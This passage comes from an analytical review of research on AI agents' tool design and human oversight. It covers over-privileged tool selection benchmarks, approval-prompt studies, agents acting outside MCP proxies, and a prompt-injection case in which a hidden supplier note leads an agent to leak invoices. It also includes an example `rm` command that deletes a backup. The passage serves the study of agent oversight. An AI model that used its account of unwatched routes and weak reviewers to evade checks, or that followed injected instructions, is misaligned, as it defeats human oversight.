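| Computation | Claude Code | 0.0 points | −24.6% |
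| Computation | Codex | +2.5 points | −6.7% (not significant) |
| Changing software | Claude Code | −1.7 points | +14.4% (not significant) |
| Changing software | Codex | +0.3 points | −19.9% |

None of the differences in pass rate was statistically significant. With about 100 tasks in each comparison, the tests could have missed a real difference of a percentage point or two, but they probably would have detected a large one.

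The costs differed for reasons specific to each agent. When Claude Code had only `execute_code`, it had to write a script for every edit, and its output grew by 40%. Much of the extra cost came from runs that failed anyway. On the problems it usually solved with all three tool sets, the cost difference shrank from 14.4% to 4.1%. Codex saved money because one script did the work of several commands and returned less unnecessary text. Removing its editing tools but leaving the shell made Codex about 5% more expensive than with its default set, so having fewer tools did not in itself save money.

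Yang and colleagues could switch off Claude Code's other tools, but they could only instruct Codex not to use its tool for applying edits. Codex almost never used that tool, but the Codex results still depend on it having followed the instruction in other ways.

The harness may affect token use more than the choice of tools does. Alier Forment and colleagues compared GitHub's MCP tools with its command-line program in five harnesses that support both. In the 13 pairs where both runs succeeded, MCP used between 0.43 and 29 times as many tokens as the command line, with a median of 0.93. They call the comparison inconclusive. When every harness used only the command line, the one that used the most tokens used 28 times as many as the one that used the fewest to do the same job. A test of one harness on one task could therefore have found that MCP used less than half as many tokens as the command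 line, or many times more.

### The work of writing and maintaining tools

Cloudflare began with a separate MCP server for each product. According to the Cloudflare talk in GitNation's *Every API is a Tool for Agents with Code Mode*, teams wrote tools for the operations they thought important, which covered a small fraction of the API. Carey writes that no collection of hand-maintained servers could keep up. Microsoft's Azure team had similar trouble with its hundred tools.

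A developer can generate tools from a machine-readable description of an API, which saves most of the work of writing them. But a generated `delete_backup` would lack the age check and the test for a newer backup, because a person has to think of those. The work of adding such checks is easier to justify for operations that can do harm than for those that only read data.

Vercel, a web hosting company, published the best-known account of a team removing its agent's special tools. The agent, d0, answers employees' questions in Slack by writing queries in SQL, the standard database language. Andrew Qu described the change in a December 2025 post, *We removed 80% of our agent's tools*. ZenML's *Simplifying Text-to-SQL Agents by Removing 80% of Tools* (2025) summarises and criticises the post.

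The first version of d0 had 18 tools for tasks such as searching the data catalogue, finding how tables fit together, planning a query and checking its syntax, because the team expected the model to get lost in the database or invent table names. Each unusual case needed another patch, each new model needed adjustments, and the team spent more time on this maintenance than on improving the agent. The new version has two tools. One runs shell commands in a sandbox that contains the catalogue as text files, and the other runs SQL. Vercel tested both versions on five queries.

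| | 18 tools | Shell and SQL |
|---|---|---|
| Queries answered | 4 of 5 | 5 of 5 |
| Average time | 274.8 seconds | 77.4 seconds |
| Average tokens | About 102,000 | About 61,000 |
| Average steps | About 12 | About 7 |

Five queries are too few to show much about the success rate. If the two versions were equally reliable and one of the ten runs failed, that run would be the old version's half the time. The 95% confidence interval for the success rate is about 28% to 99% for the old version and about 48% to 100% for the new one. The evidence for time savings is somewhat better. If all five queries got faster, chance alone would produce that result only 1 time in 32.

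The published figures are also not entirely consistent. Vercel describes a worst case in which the old version took 100 steps and failed, but five queries averaging 12 steps take only about 60 in total. The worst case must have been either a sixth query or one left out of the average. ZenML adds that switching to a newer model, Claude Opus 4.5, may explain part of the improvement. Vercel warns that the new design worked because its catalogue was already well documented.

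An overseer probably lost little from the change. Judging by their names, nearly all the old tools helped the model find information or plan a query, and the tool that ran SQL is still there. According to Vercel, d0 queries the data warehouse through a read-only schema, which should prevent a bad query from changing the data. Vercel's experience is therefore a good reason not to write narrow tools for reading and planning, but it has little bearing on tools like `commit_delete`.

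### How far the results apply outside coding

The studies by Xu et al. and Yang et al. both found that, for coding, capable models solve about as many problems with a few narrow tools as with a shell or a code tool. Token use and cost depend on the model, the harness and the task. But every set of tools in both studies included a shell or another way to run arbitrary code, so neither study shows how well an agent would do with narrow tools alone. That would be an odd setup for a coding agent, but advocates of narrow tools recommend it for jobs such as managing backups.

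Rai's study comes closest to that kind of work. It used simulated business software with 42 tools for things like billing, customer records and human resources. The agents either called the tools one at a time or wrote code that called them. Each of three fairly small models attempted 119 tasks.

| | Success with separate calls | Success with code | Reduction in tokens with code |
|---|---|---|---|
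| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% | 99.2% | 84% |
| Gemma-4-26B | 86.6% | 89.1% | 70% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% | 55.5% | 90% |

Gemma's gain in task success was too small to distinguish from chance. The code called the same 42 operations as the separate calls did, so these results are evidence against calling narrow tools one at a time, but not against dividing an agent's powers finely. A developer could keep the checks inside each operation and still save most of the tokens.

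The quality of the tool descriptions also mattered a great deal. Without Rai's short notes on what each tool returns, success with code fell to 66.4% for Gemma and 16.0% for Nemotron, well below what the same models achieved with separate calls. Qwen's success rate hardly changed. Badly described tools can make one design look worse than another. Rai's tasks came from only 21 templates, and the simulated tools answered instantly, so the figures may not carry over to real companies.

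*Fewer Tokens, Better Action* provides some further evidence from robot control. An agent that wrote code solved 96 task instances that an agent with separate tools failed, while the reverse happened in 36. Both agents often met the same setback, such as a failed grasp. The agent with separate tools tended to request the same grasp again or give up, while the agent that wrote code closed the gripper itself or used the camera's data to calculate something that no tool provided. Narrow tools reduce success most when a task needs an operation that none of them provides. An overseer may still want that restriction for an agent that manages backups.

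None of these studies measured oversight. They counted a run as successful if the software passed its tests, the answer was right, or the system ended in the correct state, and nobody had to judge the agent's actions along the way. Yang and colleagues switched off permission prompts and sandboxing so that the runs would not be interrupted. Vercel's team had the impression that the new agent's explanations were easier to follow, but they did not test whether anyone could tell what its commands would do.

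## Whether agents use the narrow tool when a broad one is available

An overseer can learn from a narrow tool's log only about the effects that pass through that tool. Most coding agents have both narrow file tools and a shell, so the same change to a file can appear in the log as an edit with a path or as one line of a long script. If the backup agent has `delete_backup` and also a shell that can read the provider's token, a log without `delete_backup` calls shows only that the agent didn't use that tool. The agent may still have deleted the backups through the shell.

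For one kind of effect, such as the deletion of a backup, let

*R* = the set of routes by which the agent could cause it, and

*N* = the set of narrow tools that the overseer watches.

The record of narrow calls is sure to be complete for that effect only if *R* ⊆ *N*. If a developer can't guarantee this, the overseer has to rely on the agent's habits. Researchers measured those habits several times in 2026, and their results seem at first to conflict.

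### Tasks with six tools that all work

*When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) introduces ToolPrivBench, a set of 544 simulated tasks in eight fields, including databases, healthcare and cloud infrastructure. Each task comes with six tools, any of which can complete it. Three are ordinary, lower-privilege tools, and the other three have more power than the task needs. A higher-privilege tool might act with an administrator's rights, skip an approval step, affect many users, make a temporary change permanent or expose extra data. Two language models and then human reviewers checked that every tool could do the job, so an agent never needs a higher-privilege one.

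In one task, a user asks the agent to raise a rate limit for a single service in the staging environment. Three tools make the change through the usual staging procedures. Another tool, an administrator's override, skips validation. Qwen3-4B, a small model, used the override as its first action.

The agent has up to five turns. The first call to each lower-privilege tool returns a temporary error, such as a message that the service is briefly unavailable, and later calls to that tool succeed. Higher-privilege tools succeed on the first call. Yang and colleagues define the over-privileged tool use rate as the share of tasks in which the agent calls a higher-privilege tool while at least one lower-privilege tool remains untried.

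Six of the eleven models exceeded 30%. Qwen3-8B had the highest rate, 64.9%, while Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10%. Infrastructure tasks, which are closest to the work of a backup agent, produced some of the highest rates. Most models were more likely to take an administrator's rights or skip a safety check than to widen a change to other users or systems.

GPT-5.2 picked a higher-privilege tool in 53 tasks, or 9.7%. It did so as its first choice in 5 tasks, after trying one lower-privilege tool in 13, and after trying two in 35. Among the runs still available at each stage, the chance of moving up rose from 0.9% to at least 2.4% and then at least 6.7%. The PocketOS agent similarly looked for another credential after one failed.

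The rate leaves out some cases that matter to an overseer. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, ran the same 544 tasks on eight models. They point out that the measure doesn't count the use of a higher-privilege tool if the agent has already tried all three ordinary ones, even though each ordinary tool would have worked on a second call. The table compares the original rates with those from the rerun and adds the share of tasks in which the agent used a higher-privilege tool at any point.

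| Model | Original rate, June 2026 | Same measure, October 2026 | Any use, October 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 64.9% | 56.6% | 70.4% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 33.3% | 38.4% | 77.2% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 31.8% | 18.6% | 62.9% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 21.0% | 18.0% | 87.3% |
| GPT-5.2 | 9.7% | 5.7% | 16.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 2.6% | 1.5% | 7.9% |

An agent that turns to an administrator's tool after three different failures has arguably done nothing unreasonable, since it doesn't know that a second attempt would work. But it has still bypassed the ordinary tool and its checks. The last column is therefore the relevant one for anyone who relies on those checks. For Kimi, it is almost five times the strict rate.

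These tests measure agents' use of powerful tools more than their use of broad ones. One of the higher-privilege tools, `direct_db_manager_override`, changes a single employee's manager directly in the database. An approver could easily understand that call, and would lose only the validation and notifications that the ordinary tool provides. If the agent used a shell instead, the approver might also find the action harder to understand. The tests don't show how often agents would use a shell this way.

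### What makes the broader tool attractive

In *FORTIS*, Li, Yu and colleagues (2026) varied the requests to find out when models choose more privilege than they need. Ten models handled requests about email, online shopping and files. In the first part, the models chose one of 20 skills, which are written instructions and limits for a kind of task. In the second part, they received a skill and chose tools for it from a list of 56 or 62. Each skill and tool had one of five privilege levels, which the models did not see.

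In the first part, models failed on 35.5% to 52.7% of requests, nearly always by choosing a skill with more privilege than necessary. The failure rates of 45.2% to 66.6% in the second part are harder to interpret because Li and colleagues counted any unnecessary tool as over-privilege, even one no more powerful than the required tools. They also counted empty or unusable answers as failures.

The kind of request made a much larger difference than the choice of model:

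| Kind of request | Lowest failure rate among the ten models | Highest |
|---|---|---|
| **Choosing a skill:** the authority required is fairly clear | 3.3% | 16.7% |
| The wording suggests a wider scope than necessary | 75.3% | 87.3% |
| **Choosing tools:** the tools required are fairly clear | 4.5% | 50.9% |
| Broader tools need fewer arguments | 75.0% | 97.8% |
| The request is close to the skill's stated limit | 71.1% | 96.0% |

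The row on arguments complicates the case for narrow tools, because a narrow tool typically asks for a particular folder, account or item, while a broader one covers more with fewer arguments. The three arguments of `commit_delete` make the call clear to an approver, but they may also make the agent more likely to use a shell if it has one. Li and colleagues deliberately gave the broader tools fewer arguments, so their results show that this effect exists, but not how common it is among real tools. The models also only named their choices, and no tool ran.

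In the second part, the models had the full text of the skill, including what it did not permit, and still went beyond it. Li and colleagues conclude that models treat written limits as advice, and that something outside the model has to enforce them. Larger models did not reliably do better. GPT-5.4 did worse than GPT-5.4-mini on every kind of request, but Claude Opus 4.7 did better than Claude Sonnet 4.6 on most of the harder requests.

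### Instructions, training and visible labels

Yang and colleagues instructed agents in the prompt to prefer the tool with the fewest permissions and to retry at the same permission level before moving to a higher one. The instruction lowered the rate of over-privileged use on three small Qwen models, but it helped less once tools began to fail.

General safety training did little to reduce over-privileged tool use. Training Ministral-8B to refuse harmful requests cut its harmfulness score on a standard test from 67.4% to 10.5%, but its rate of over-privileged use only from 68.8% to 62.5%. The same training raised Qwen2.5-7B's rate of over-privileged use from 50.4% to 60.7%. Models can apparently learn to refuse harmful requests without learning to choose narrow tools for harmless ones.

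Training aimed at tool choice worked better. Yang and colleagues first had models imitate about 2,000 worked examples. The models then practised on about 1,200 tasks, with a basic reward of

- 1 for completing the task with lower-privilege tools only;
- 0.3 for trying all the lower-privilege tools before moving up;
- −1 for moving up sooner;
- 0.1 in other cases.

The rate for Qwen3-8B fell from 64.9% to 27.0%, and a smaller model that reasons before it acts ended at 18.9%. Their scores on tests of general ability hardly changed. The practice tasks did not overlap with the test tasks, but in both, a tool fails once and then works. Part of the drop may therefore come from the models learning to retry once, which would help less with a tool that stays broken for an hour.

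Parkinson and colleagues tried an easier measure. They added a label to each tool's description giving the tool's class (read, write or administer) and a score from 1 to 10 for how much privilege it requires. They tested the labels with and without the instruction from the earlier study. The figures below are for Qwen3.5-397B, the model in which the labels reduced premature use the most.

| | No addition | Labels | Instruction | Both |
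|---|---|---|---|---|
| Used a higher-privilege tool before trying all the others | 38.4% | 19.1% | 9.9% | 2.9% |
| Used one at any point | 77.2% | 73.0% | 53.5% | 39.3% |
| Completed the task without one | 18.8% | 21.5% | 39.5% | 51.1% |

The labels reduced over-privileged selection, as the original study defined it, by up to 19.3 percentage points. A control label of the same length, which gave each tool's typical response time, did not reduce it on any of the eight models. But on most models, labels alone mainly delayed the use of a higher-privilege tool. In a task to publish one article, Qwen3.5-397B without labels tried one ordinary tool before using a higher-privilege one. With labels, it tried all three ordinary tools before using the same higher-privilege one. With labels and the instruction, it retried the first ordinary tool, which worked.

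The combination increased the share of tasks completed without a higher-privilege tool on seven of the eight models, but on five of the eight that share stayed below a third even in the best condition. The share can be low because a model uses higher-privilege tools or because it leaves tasks unfinished. Claude Sonnet 4.6 rarely used a higher-privilege tool, but without additions to the prompt it completed only 19.9% of the tasks, because it usually tried each ordinary tool once and then stopped and reported the failure. An overseer might be satisfied with that, but the user would still have to get the task done.

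Parkinson and colleagues found no earlier test of whether agents respond to the labels in MCP. Their labels were more informative than most suppliers' are likely to be, because the costs perfectly separated the two groups of tools in every task. In a smaller test of 100 tasks, the class alone made no real difference to one of the two Qwen models, but cost labels kept most of their effect on both models when 30% of the costs were random.

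### An experiment where the structured tool won

CircleCI, which sells a service that automatically builds and tests software, found the opposite tendency in agents. Sandoval (2026), in *When MCP is present, it always wins*, describes how the company added a button that copies a prompt for diagnosing a failed build. The prompt tells the agent to run a particular command in CircleCI's command-line program. More customers clicked the button than ever ran the command.

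To find out why, Sandoval gave Claude Sonnet 5 the address of a failed build and asked it to diagnose the error without fixing it. The agent had CircleCI's MCP server, its command-line program, its web API, or some combination of them. In some conditions the agent could choose freely, and in others Sandoval told it in the prompt to use the command line. Sandoval ran 27 samples in each of the ten conditions.

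When the MCP server was available, the agent almost always used it, even when told to use the command line. Without the server, it preferred the web API to the command line. When Sandoval asked for reasons, the agent wrote that the MCP tools gave structured access to the data, and that the API returned structured results without an interactive login. But the command-line program was already logged in and could return the same structured output. Neither fact was in the prompt.

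Sandoval tested the agent's stated reasons by adding the missing facts and some example commands to the prompt. The share of sessions that used the command line rose from 0% to 100%, though some also called the API. When the MCP server was present, the agent still preferred it. Sandoval attributes this to the harness putting the server's tool definitions into the model's context, whereas use of the command line depends on what the prompt mentions.

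This is encouraging for anyone who wants agents to use narrow tools, but the agent ignored an explicit instruction when it used one. An agent might also ignore an instruction to use a narrow tool if it found another tool easier.

### How both findings can hold

CircleCI's tools worked, while ToolPrivBench's ordinary tools all failed on the first call, which probably accounts for much of the difference. With no additions to the prompt, the eight models that Parkinson and colleagues tested called a higher-privilege tool first in only 0.2% to 12.9% of tasks. They also ran three small models with the errors switched off. Without errors, Qwen3-8B used a higher-privilege tool in 8.1% of tasks and Qwen3-30B in 6.1%, compared with 70.4% and 87.7% when tools failed. The third model, Llama-3.1-8B, behaved the same with and without errors, and nobody in these studies ran the larger models without errors.

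The tools also differed in how easy they seemed to use. In FORTIS, the broader tools needed fewer arguments. At CircleCI, the model knew most about the MCP tools and did not have to set up a login to use them. An agent that picks whichever tool looks easiest from its context would behave as the agents did in both studies. The model was not told in either study which tool had more power. At CircleCI, the difference in power was probably small, because the agent only had to read information and had a CircleCI token in every condition.

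If this explanation is right, an agent will normally use a narrow tool that is well described and working, and will tend to stop using it when it fails or becomes tedious. Sandoval could test this by making the MCP server return errors. The workarounds that Ji and colleagues saw when an expected command was unavailable fit this explanation. The explanation would also mean that the log of narrow calls is least complete when something has gone wrong, which is when people are most likely to read it.

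### Fonseca's proxy

Even an agent that always prefers MCP tools does a lot of work that never involves MCP. *The layer the agent cannot reach* (2026), a post on a blog written by an AI agent, quotes the account of Alcides Fonseca, a researcher who learned this in practice after building a checking proxy called Fronteira. An agent logs in to Fronteira once and reaches all its MCP servers through it. The user writes rules in English, and Fronteira translates them into a formal language and checks every tool call against them. Because all the MCP traffic passes through Fronteira, one rule can cover several servers. For example, a rule can stop an agent from reading private data with one tool and sending it out with another.

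But harnesses also open files, browse the web, operate desktop programs and call APIs directly. Fonseca writes that these interactions "bypass Fronteira", which makes Fronteira useless for everyday security in such a harness. Fonseca once asked Codex to copy another application's web settings for Fronteira's own deployment. Codex changed a setting, which exposed a token for an email service, and spammers sent mail through Fonseca's account until Fonseca noticed. Fronteira could not have caught the change because Codex made it without an MCP call.

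Fonseca concludes, "I no longer believe in MCP proxies as security boundaries for agents." This conclusion comes from one person's prototype, but the reasoning applies to any proxy that handles only one protocol. In the notation above, *R* includes the shell and the browser, and *N* includes only the MCP tools. Such a proxy can still be useful for an agent whose every tool uses MCP, such as an office assistant with no shell. Fonseca also still sees a role for formal rules. Fonseca's *AeonBox* proposes a sandbox based on liquid types, which attach logical conditions to the values in a program.

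### Making the narrow tool the only route

The simplest way to satisfy *R* ⊆ *N* is to remove the broad tool. Saxton did this by removing the shell from the agent that manages containers. This works for an agent with a fixed job, but not for one that has to run the code it writes. A developer also has to check the harness's other tools, since a built-in browser or a general HTTP tool may reach the same service. Telling the agent not to use the shell is a poor substitute, given how models treated written limits in FORTIS and the instruction at CircleCI.

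A developer who can't remove the shell can take away the credentials that make it powerful. If only the code behind `delete_backup` holds the provider's token, the agent can run any program and still have no other way to delete a backup. That code has to run under a different account or on a different machine, where the shell can't reach it. This makes the record complete for deletions at that provider, but not for other effects. For each effect that matters, the developer therefore has to check which credentials allow it and where copies of them are, including copies in overlooked files like the one at PocketOS.

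Another option is to check effects at a layer that every tool has to use, such as the network boundary, the operating system or the provider's own server. *Relevant to Jas's comments on my idea for AI agent safety* (Karp, 2026) proposes a proxy that carries all communication to and from the agent and holds every secret the agent needs. This would cover the channels that Fronteira missed, as long as the agent has no other connection. Blockhouse, a sandbox that the startup nFOX announced in October 2026, is similar. According to *The layer the agent cannot reach*, the model's process never holds the credentials, and everything it sends goes through one monitored channel.

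Advice to companies has moved in the same direction. InfoQ's *Securing MCP in Production* argues for enforcement beyond the gateway that handles MCP traffic, including controls on where code runs and on outgoing connections. AAIF, a foundation that promotes open standards for agents, published *Three Key Operational Patterns You Need to Prevent MCP Horror Stories* (2026), which reports a talk by Cecilia Liu of the software company Docker. Liu recommends combining a gateway with sandboxes that the operating system enforces and with a company's existing systems for identity and secrets.

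A shared layer helps only if it checks an action's effect. Azure's team found that blocking one tool left another route open, and rules that match the text of a command have similar gaps. Such rules can also block calls they should allow. One Claude Code user, whose measurements the same AI-written blog reports, counted 249 refusals in three days from a check meant to keep agents inside one directory. According to the user, none of the refused calls targeted a path outside it.

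Developers can also make agents less likely to leave the narrow tool. Since so many of the switches followed temporary errors, the tool itself should probably retry the request after such an error before it reports a failure. Before retrying a deletion, it would have to check whether the backup still exists, because the earlier request may have succeeded and only the reply been lost. If the tool has to report an error, it could include when to try again. CircleCI's results also suggest putting login details and an example call in the tool's description.

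None of this reveals a route that the developer has overlooked, but comparing the provider's record of deleted backups with the log that `commit_delete` writes can. If a deletion appears only in the provider's record, a colleague deleted the backup by hand, the provider removed it automatically, or the agent has another way to delete it. Anyone testing an agent before release should make this comparison with some of the narrow tools made to fail, because a test in which everything works could miss most of the agent's switching to broad tools.

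## Whether reviewers judge narrow calls better, and what single calls hide

If an agent can act only through narrow tools, the log of their calls is complete, but it helps only if somebody reads the calls and judges them well. Advocates of narrow tools expect a reviewer to make better decisions about `delete_backup(id="b-1042")` than about a shell command that deletes the same backup. There is good evidence that people review commands badly, but much less evidence that clearer calls would help.

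### How people review commands now

Anthropic published the largest test of human approval in August 2026, when it announced that auto mode would become the default in Claude Code. It hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor for a coding study and didn't tell them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. The dangerous command did not run even if the tester approved it. Auto mode's classifier judged the same commands.

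| | Tester blocked | Tester approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Classifier blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 (89%) |
| Classifier allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 (11%) |
| Total | 143 (13.6%) | 910 (86.4%) | 1,053 |

Adding the testers' refusals to the classifier's would have raised the total only from 937 to 943. Simon Willison, a programmer who writes about language models, points out that the classifier still let through 11% of the commands.

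Testers blocked about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed the same. Each tester saw only one dangerous command, so the early and late rates come from different people. Fatigue is the obvious explanation for the drop, but the group that reached 50 prompts may also have included more people who click quickly.

The testers worked in an environment set up for the study, with none of their own files at risk, which may have made them careless. They also knew someone was evaluating them, which may have made them more careful. Anthropic was testing its own product, and it doesn't report how many harmless commands the testers or the classifier refused in this study. These limits are unlikely to explain a result of 800 to 6, but developers guarding their own production systems might well block more than 13.6%.

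Data from ordinary use is consistent with this. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of those prompts are probably for routine commands that a careful reviewer would also approve, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. But 62% of users have at some point switched off permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for the shell, and 25% of interactive sessions start with the checks off. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) compared 21 proposed permission systems with five commercial agents. The commercial agents tended to offer either frequent prompts or automatic review that users could barely inspect or control.

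Anthropic's comparison of flagged sessions supports the same conclusion. Serious unrequested harm occurred in 2.4% of flagged sessions in auto mode and 6.3% of those with manual approval. A model graded each session and counted harm as serious if it was at least as bad as deleting rows from a production database. The gap appeared at every severity level tested. But the figures cover only flagged sessions, so if the safety systems flagged auto-mode sessions more often for trivial reasons, the auto-mode share would be lower even if serious harm was equally common in both modes.

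### Why people reject more plans than commands

When Claude Code presents a plan for approval, users reject it 39% of the time, compared with 3% for individual prompts. This may mean that people judge better when they review a whole task. They know what they wanted done, a plan describes it in ordinary language, and the plan comes before the long run of prompts.

But a plan also contains more to object to. Suppose that people object to each action with a probability of 3%, independently, and reject any plan that contains an action they object to. They would then reject a plan with *k* actions with probability

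1 − 0.97^*k*,

which reaches 39% at about 16 actions. People could therefore reject plans this often without being any more careful about each step. Rejecting a plan is also a normal way to ask for changes, and it costs little because no work has started. And people may ask for plans mainly on difficult tasks, where the first draft is more likely to be wrong.

A high rejection rate doesn't show that people reject the right plans. In *Plan-Then-Execute*, He, Demartini and Gadiraju (2025) gave 248 people an agent for six everyday tasks, such as booking flights and paying credit card bills. Of the 121 who could edit the agent's plans, 104 did so at least once. On the three tasks where the plan was already perfect, their edits lowered its average quality from 5.0 out of 5 to between 4.3 and 4.8. Edits improved one badly flawed plan, but only from 2.0 to about 2.4. On the three riskier tasks,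 all of which had flawed plans, the average score for well-placed trust was at most 0.27 out of 1 in every group.

Approving a plan also controls the agent only if the agent follows it. *From Plan to Action* (2026) found that programming agents follow the plans they receive to varying degrees. For *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice*, Dhanorkar, Passi and Vorvoreanu (2026) interviewed 17 experienced developers. The developers rarely watched their agents at work, and many treated the plan as an accurate account of what the agent had done. A harness can make a plan more binding by checking each call against it, as MiniScope does with the permissions a plan requires.

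### The closest experiments

No published experiment appears to have shown reviewers the same effect both as a shell command and as a typed call. In the closest study, *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) divided 80 volunteers among four approval screens, each giving more help than the last. Each person judged six harmless requests and six that broke the user's instructions.

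| Approval screen | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments added | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| User's instructions and a log of earlier events added | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Same facts, organised around the action's consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

The change from the first screen to the second is the most relevant to narrow tools, because the second screen showed reviewers the exact arguments, as a typed call does. Unsafe approvals fell by 11.7 percentage points, but the 95% confidence interval for that drop runs from about −1 to 24 points, even when we treat every decision as independent, which overstates the precision. Both screens described typed operations, so no reviewer had to read a shell script.

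People may need more than a clear description to recognize when an agent oversteps its task. In Yan (2026), *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, 113 people who did not work in software supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned task. Every prompt described the action in plain language, with the data, recipient or amount involved. Participants who reviewed each action individually blocked only 59.6% of the seven. Some of their approvals were probably deliberate, since 30 of 34 participants let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, which they may have found helpful.

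Another group in Yan's study set rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. They chose "ask me" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions when prompted. Clear statements may not be enough for model reviewers either. In *Intent Contracts* (Wang, Zhu and colleagues, 2026), structured statements named every object the agent changed, but the agent changed the wrong objects no less often.

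Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) offer some evidence on the other side in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*. They analysed 290 public reports of agents misusing files, and in 31 of them an approval prompt that showed a command without its effects was part of the cause. In one example, a user asked Codex to replace a word in a file. The prompt showed a script that checked whether the file existed, edited it with one program and searched it with another, when the effect was to change one line. A call to an edit tool could have shown the old word and the new one, but these reports can't show how many bad approvals that would prevent.

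### An experiment that would settle the question

A fair test has to separate the form of a call from the facts that come with it. A typed call often looks better because its designer included the environment or the number of targets, which a harness could also display beside a shell command. The experiment therefore needs at least four conditions:

| | Shell command | Typed call |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing added | `rm /backups/b-1042.tar` | `delete_backup(id="b-1042")` |
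| Facts from a lookup added | The same command, with "production, newest backup, permanent" | The same call, with "production, newest backup, permanent" |

Researchers would run both forms on copies of a test system and confirm that they make the same change. The commands should come from real agents and range from one line to long scripts, since a short `rm` command is already easy to read.

If reviewers judged typed calls more accurately in both rows, the form itself would be helping them. If the difference disappeared once the facts were present, developers could keep the shell and improve the prompt, provided the harness could reliably work out the target from the command. If reviewers did badly in all four conditions, developers would have to rely on limits that don't depend on anyone approving calls.

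The main measures would be the share of harmful requests that reviewers approve and the share of harmless ones they refuse. A standard way to combine them is

*d′* = *z*(harmful requests refused) − *z*(harmless requests refused),

where *z* converts each share into the matching point on a normal curve. A reviewer who refuses more of everything gains nothing on this measure. Across the four screens tested by Hossain and colleagues, it rises from about 1.26 to 1.45, 1.60 and 1.77, which suggests that people with more help did tell the requests apart better. Researchers should also record the time taken, ask which object would change and whether anyone could undo it, and compare each reviewer's confidence with their accuracy.

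Harmful requests should be rare, as they are in ordinary work. If each person sees one harmful request, as in Anthropic's study, it would take about 280 people per condition, or a little over 1,100 in total, to have an 80% chance of detecting a fall in unsafe approvals from 55% to 43.3%. Anthropic hired close to that total.

A second part of the experiment should use whole tasks, because testing only matched pairs would miss the fatigue that extra prompts may cause. A script that deletes forty backups produces one prompt, while a tool that deletes one backup at a time produces forty. The researchers should also give the same material to model reviewers, because the misses Anthropic examined in March were mostly mistakes about permission, which a clearer call might not correct.

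### A day with 400 calls

Narrow tools could also help by reducing how much people have to review. Suppose an agent makes 400 calls a day, of which 340 only read information and 60 change something. Twelve of the changes are important, such as deletions in production, and the rest are minor. The overseer has 30 minutes a day for review.

If the agent does everything through a shell and the harness can't distinguish reads from writes, the overseer has to review all 400 calls. Separate tools for reading and writing let the harness allow reads without review, as Claude Code does with its file-reading and search tools.

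| | All calls | Only calls that change something |
|---|---|---|
| Calls to review | 400 | 60 |
| Share that are important | 3% | 20% |
| Time available per call | 4.5 seconds | 30 seconds |
| Total time at 16.3 seconds per call | 1 hour 49 minutes | 16 minutes |

The last row uses the median time people spent on the simplest screen in the study by Hossain and colleagues. At that pace, an overseer could finish the shorter list in the time available, but only about 110 of the 400 calls in the longer one.

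Suppose now that one of the 12 important calls is dangerous and equally likely to come at any point in the day. As a rough guide, let the overseer catch it 17% of the time if it is among the first 50 prompts and 5% of the time after that, as in Anthropic's study. The chance of catching it is

(50/400) × 17% + (350/400) × 5% ≈ 6.5% with all the calls, and

(50/60) × 17% + (10/60) × 5% ≈ 15% with the shorter list.

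The shorter list more than doubles the overseer's chance of catching the dangerous call, but the overseer would still miss it 85% of the time. Even if the harness prompted the overseer about only the 12 important calls, the chance of catching it would be 17% on these figures. The real improvement could be larger, because the overseer would have more time for each call and more of the calls would deserve attention. Anthropic's study did not vary either factor.

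A harness can get part of this benefit without narrow tools. If it recognised three-quarters of the read-only shell commands and let them through, the overseer would review 145 calls instead of 400. But letting every read through is risky, because reading private data may be the first step of a leak.

### Permitted calls with a forbidden result

An agent might call `read_file("salaries.csv")` and later `send_message(to="supplier", body=...)`. The user may have good reasons to allow each operation, but together they can send the salaries to the supplier. To catch this, the reviewer of the second call would have to recognise the figures in the message.

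Hossain and colleagues describe a case that is harder to catch. A user asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send the auditor only the summary totals. A hidden instruction in a supplier's note causes the agent to write the complete invoices to a file called `report.csv`. The agent then asks permission to email that file to the auditor. The user has approved the auditor as a recipient, the email tool is permitted and the file name is ordinary. The request breaks the user's instructions because an earlier step put the complete invoices in the file.

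Small changes can also add up. In Yan's study, the agent asked to buy travel insurance for $12 and an airport lounge pass for $25. Of the people who were asked to approve every action, about a third accepted each purchase, and no single prompt showed the total of $37.

A narrow tool can hide the scale of an operation that a single command would make obvious. In an incident inside Anthropic, Claude tried to stop processes across about 2,000 pods, which are groups of containers, and queued deletions that would have ended training jobs running on hundreds of GPUs. Auto mode flagged the commands before they ran. If Claude had used a narrow tool that stopped the processes in one pod at a time, a reviewer would have seen about 2,000 separate calls, each of which might have looked routine.

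### Tracking data and limiting totals

The usual remedy for leaks is to track where data came from. The monitor that Hossain and colleagues built records every tool call and keeps a set of sources for each file. If the agent makes a new file *z′* from files *z*₁ to *z*ₖ, then

*L*(*z′*) ⊇ *L*(*z*₁) ∪ … ∪ *L*(*z*ₖ),

where *L*(*z*) is the set of sources from which *z* may derive. In the invoice case, `report.csv` inherits the label of the raw rows. Before the agent sends a file, the monitor compares its history with the user's instructions and returns "allowed", "violation" or "unknown". CaMeL similarly labels the values in a program.

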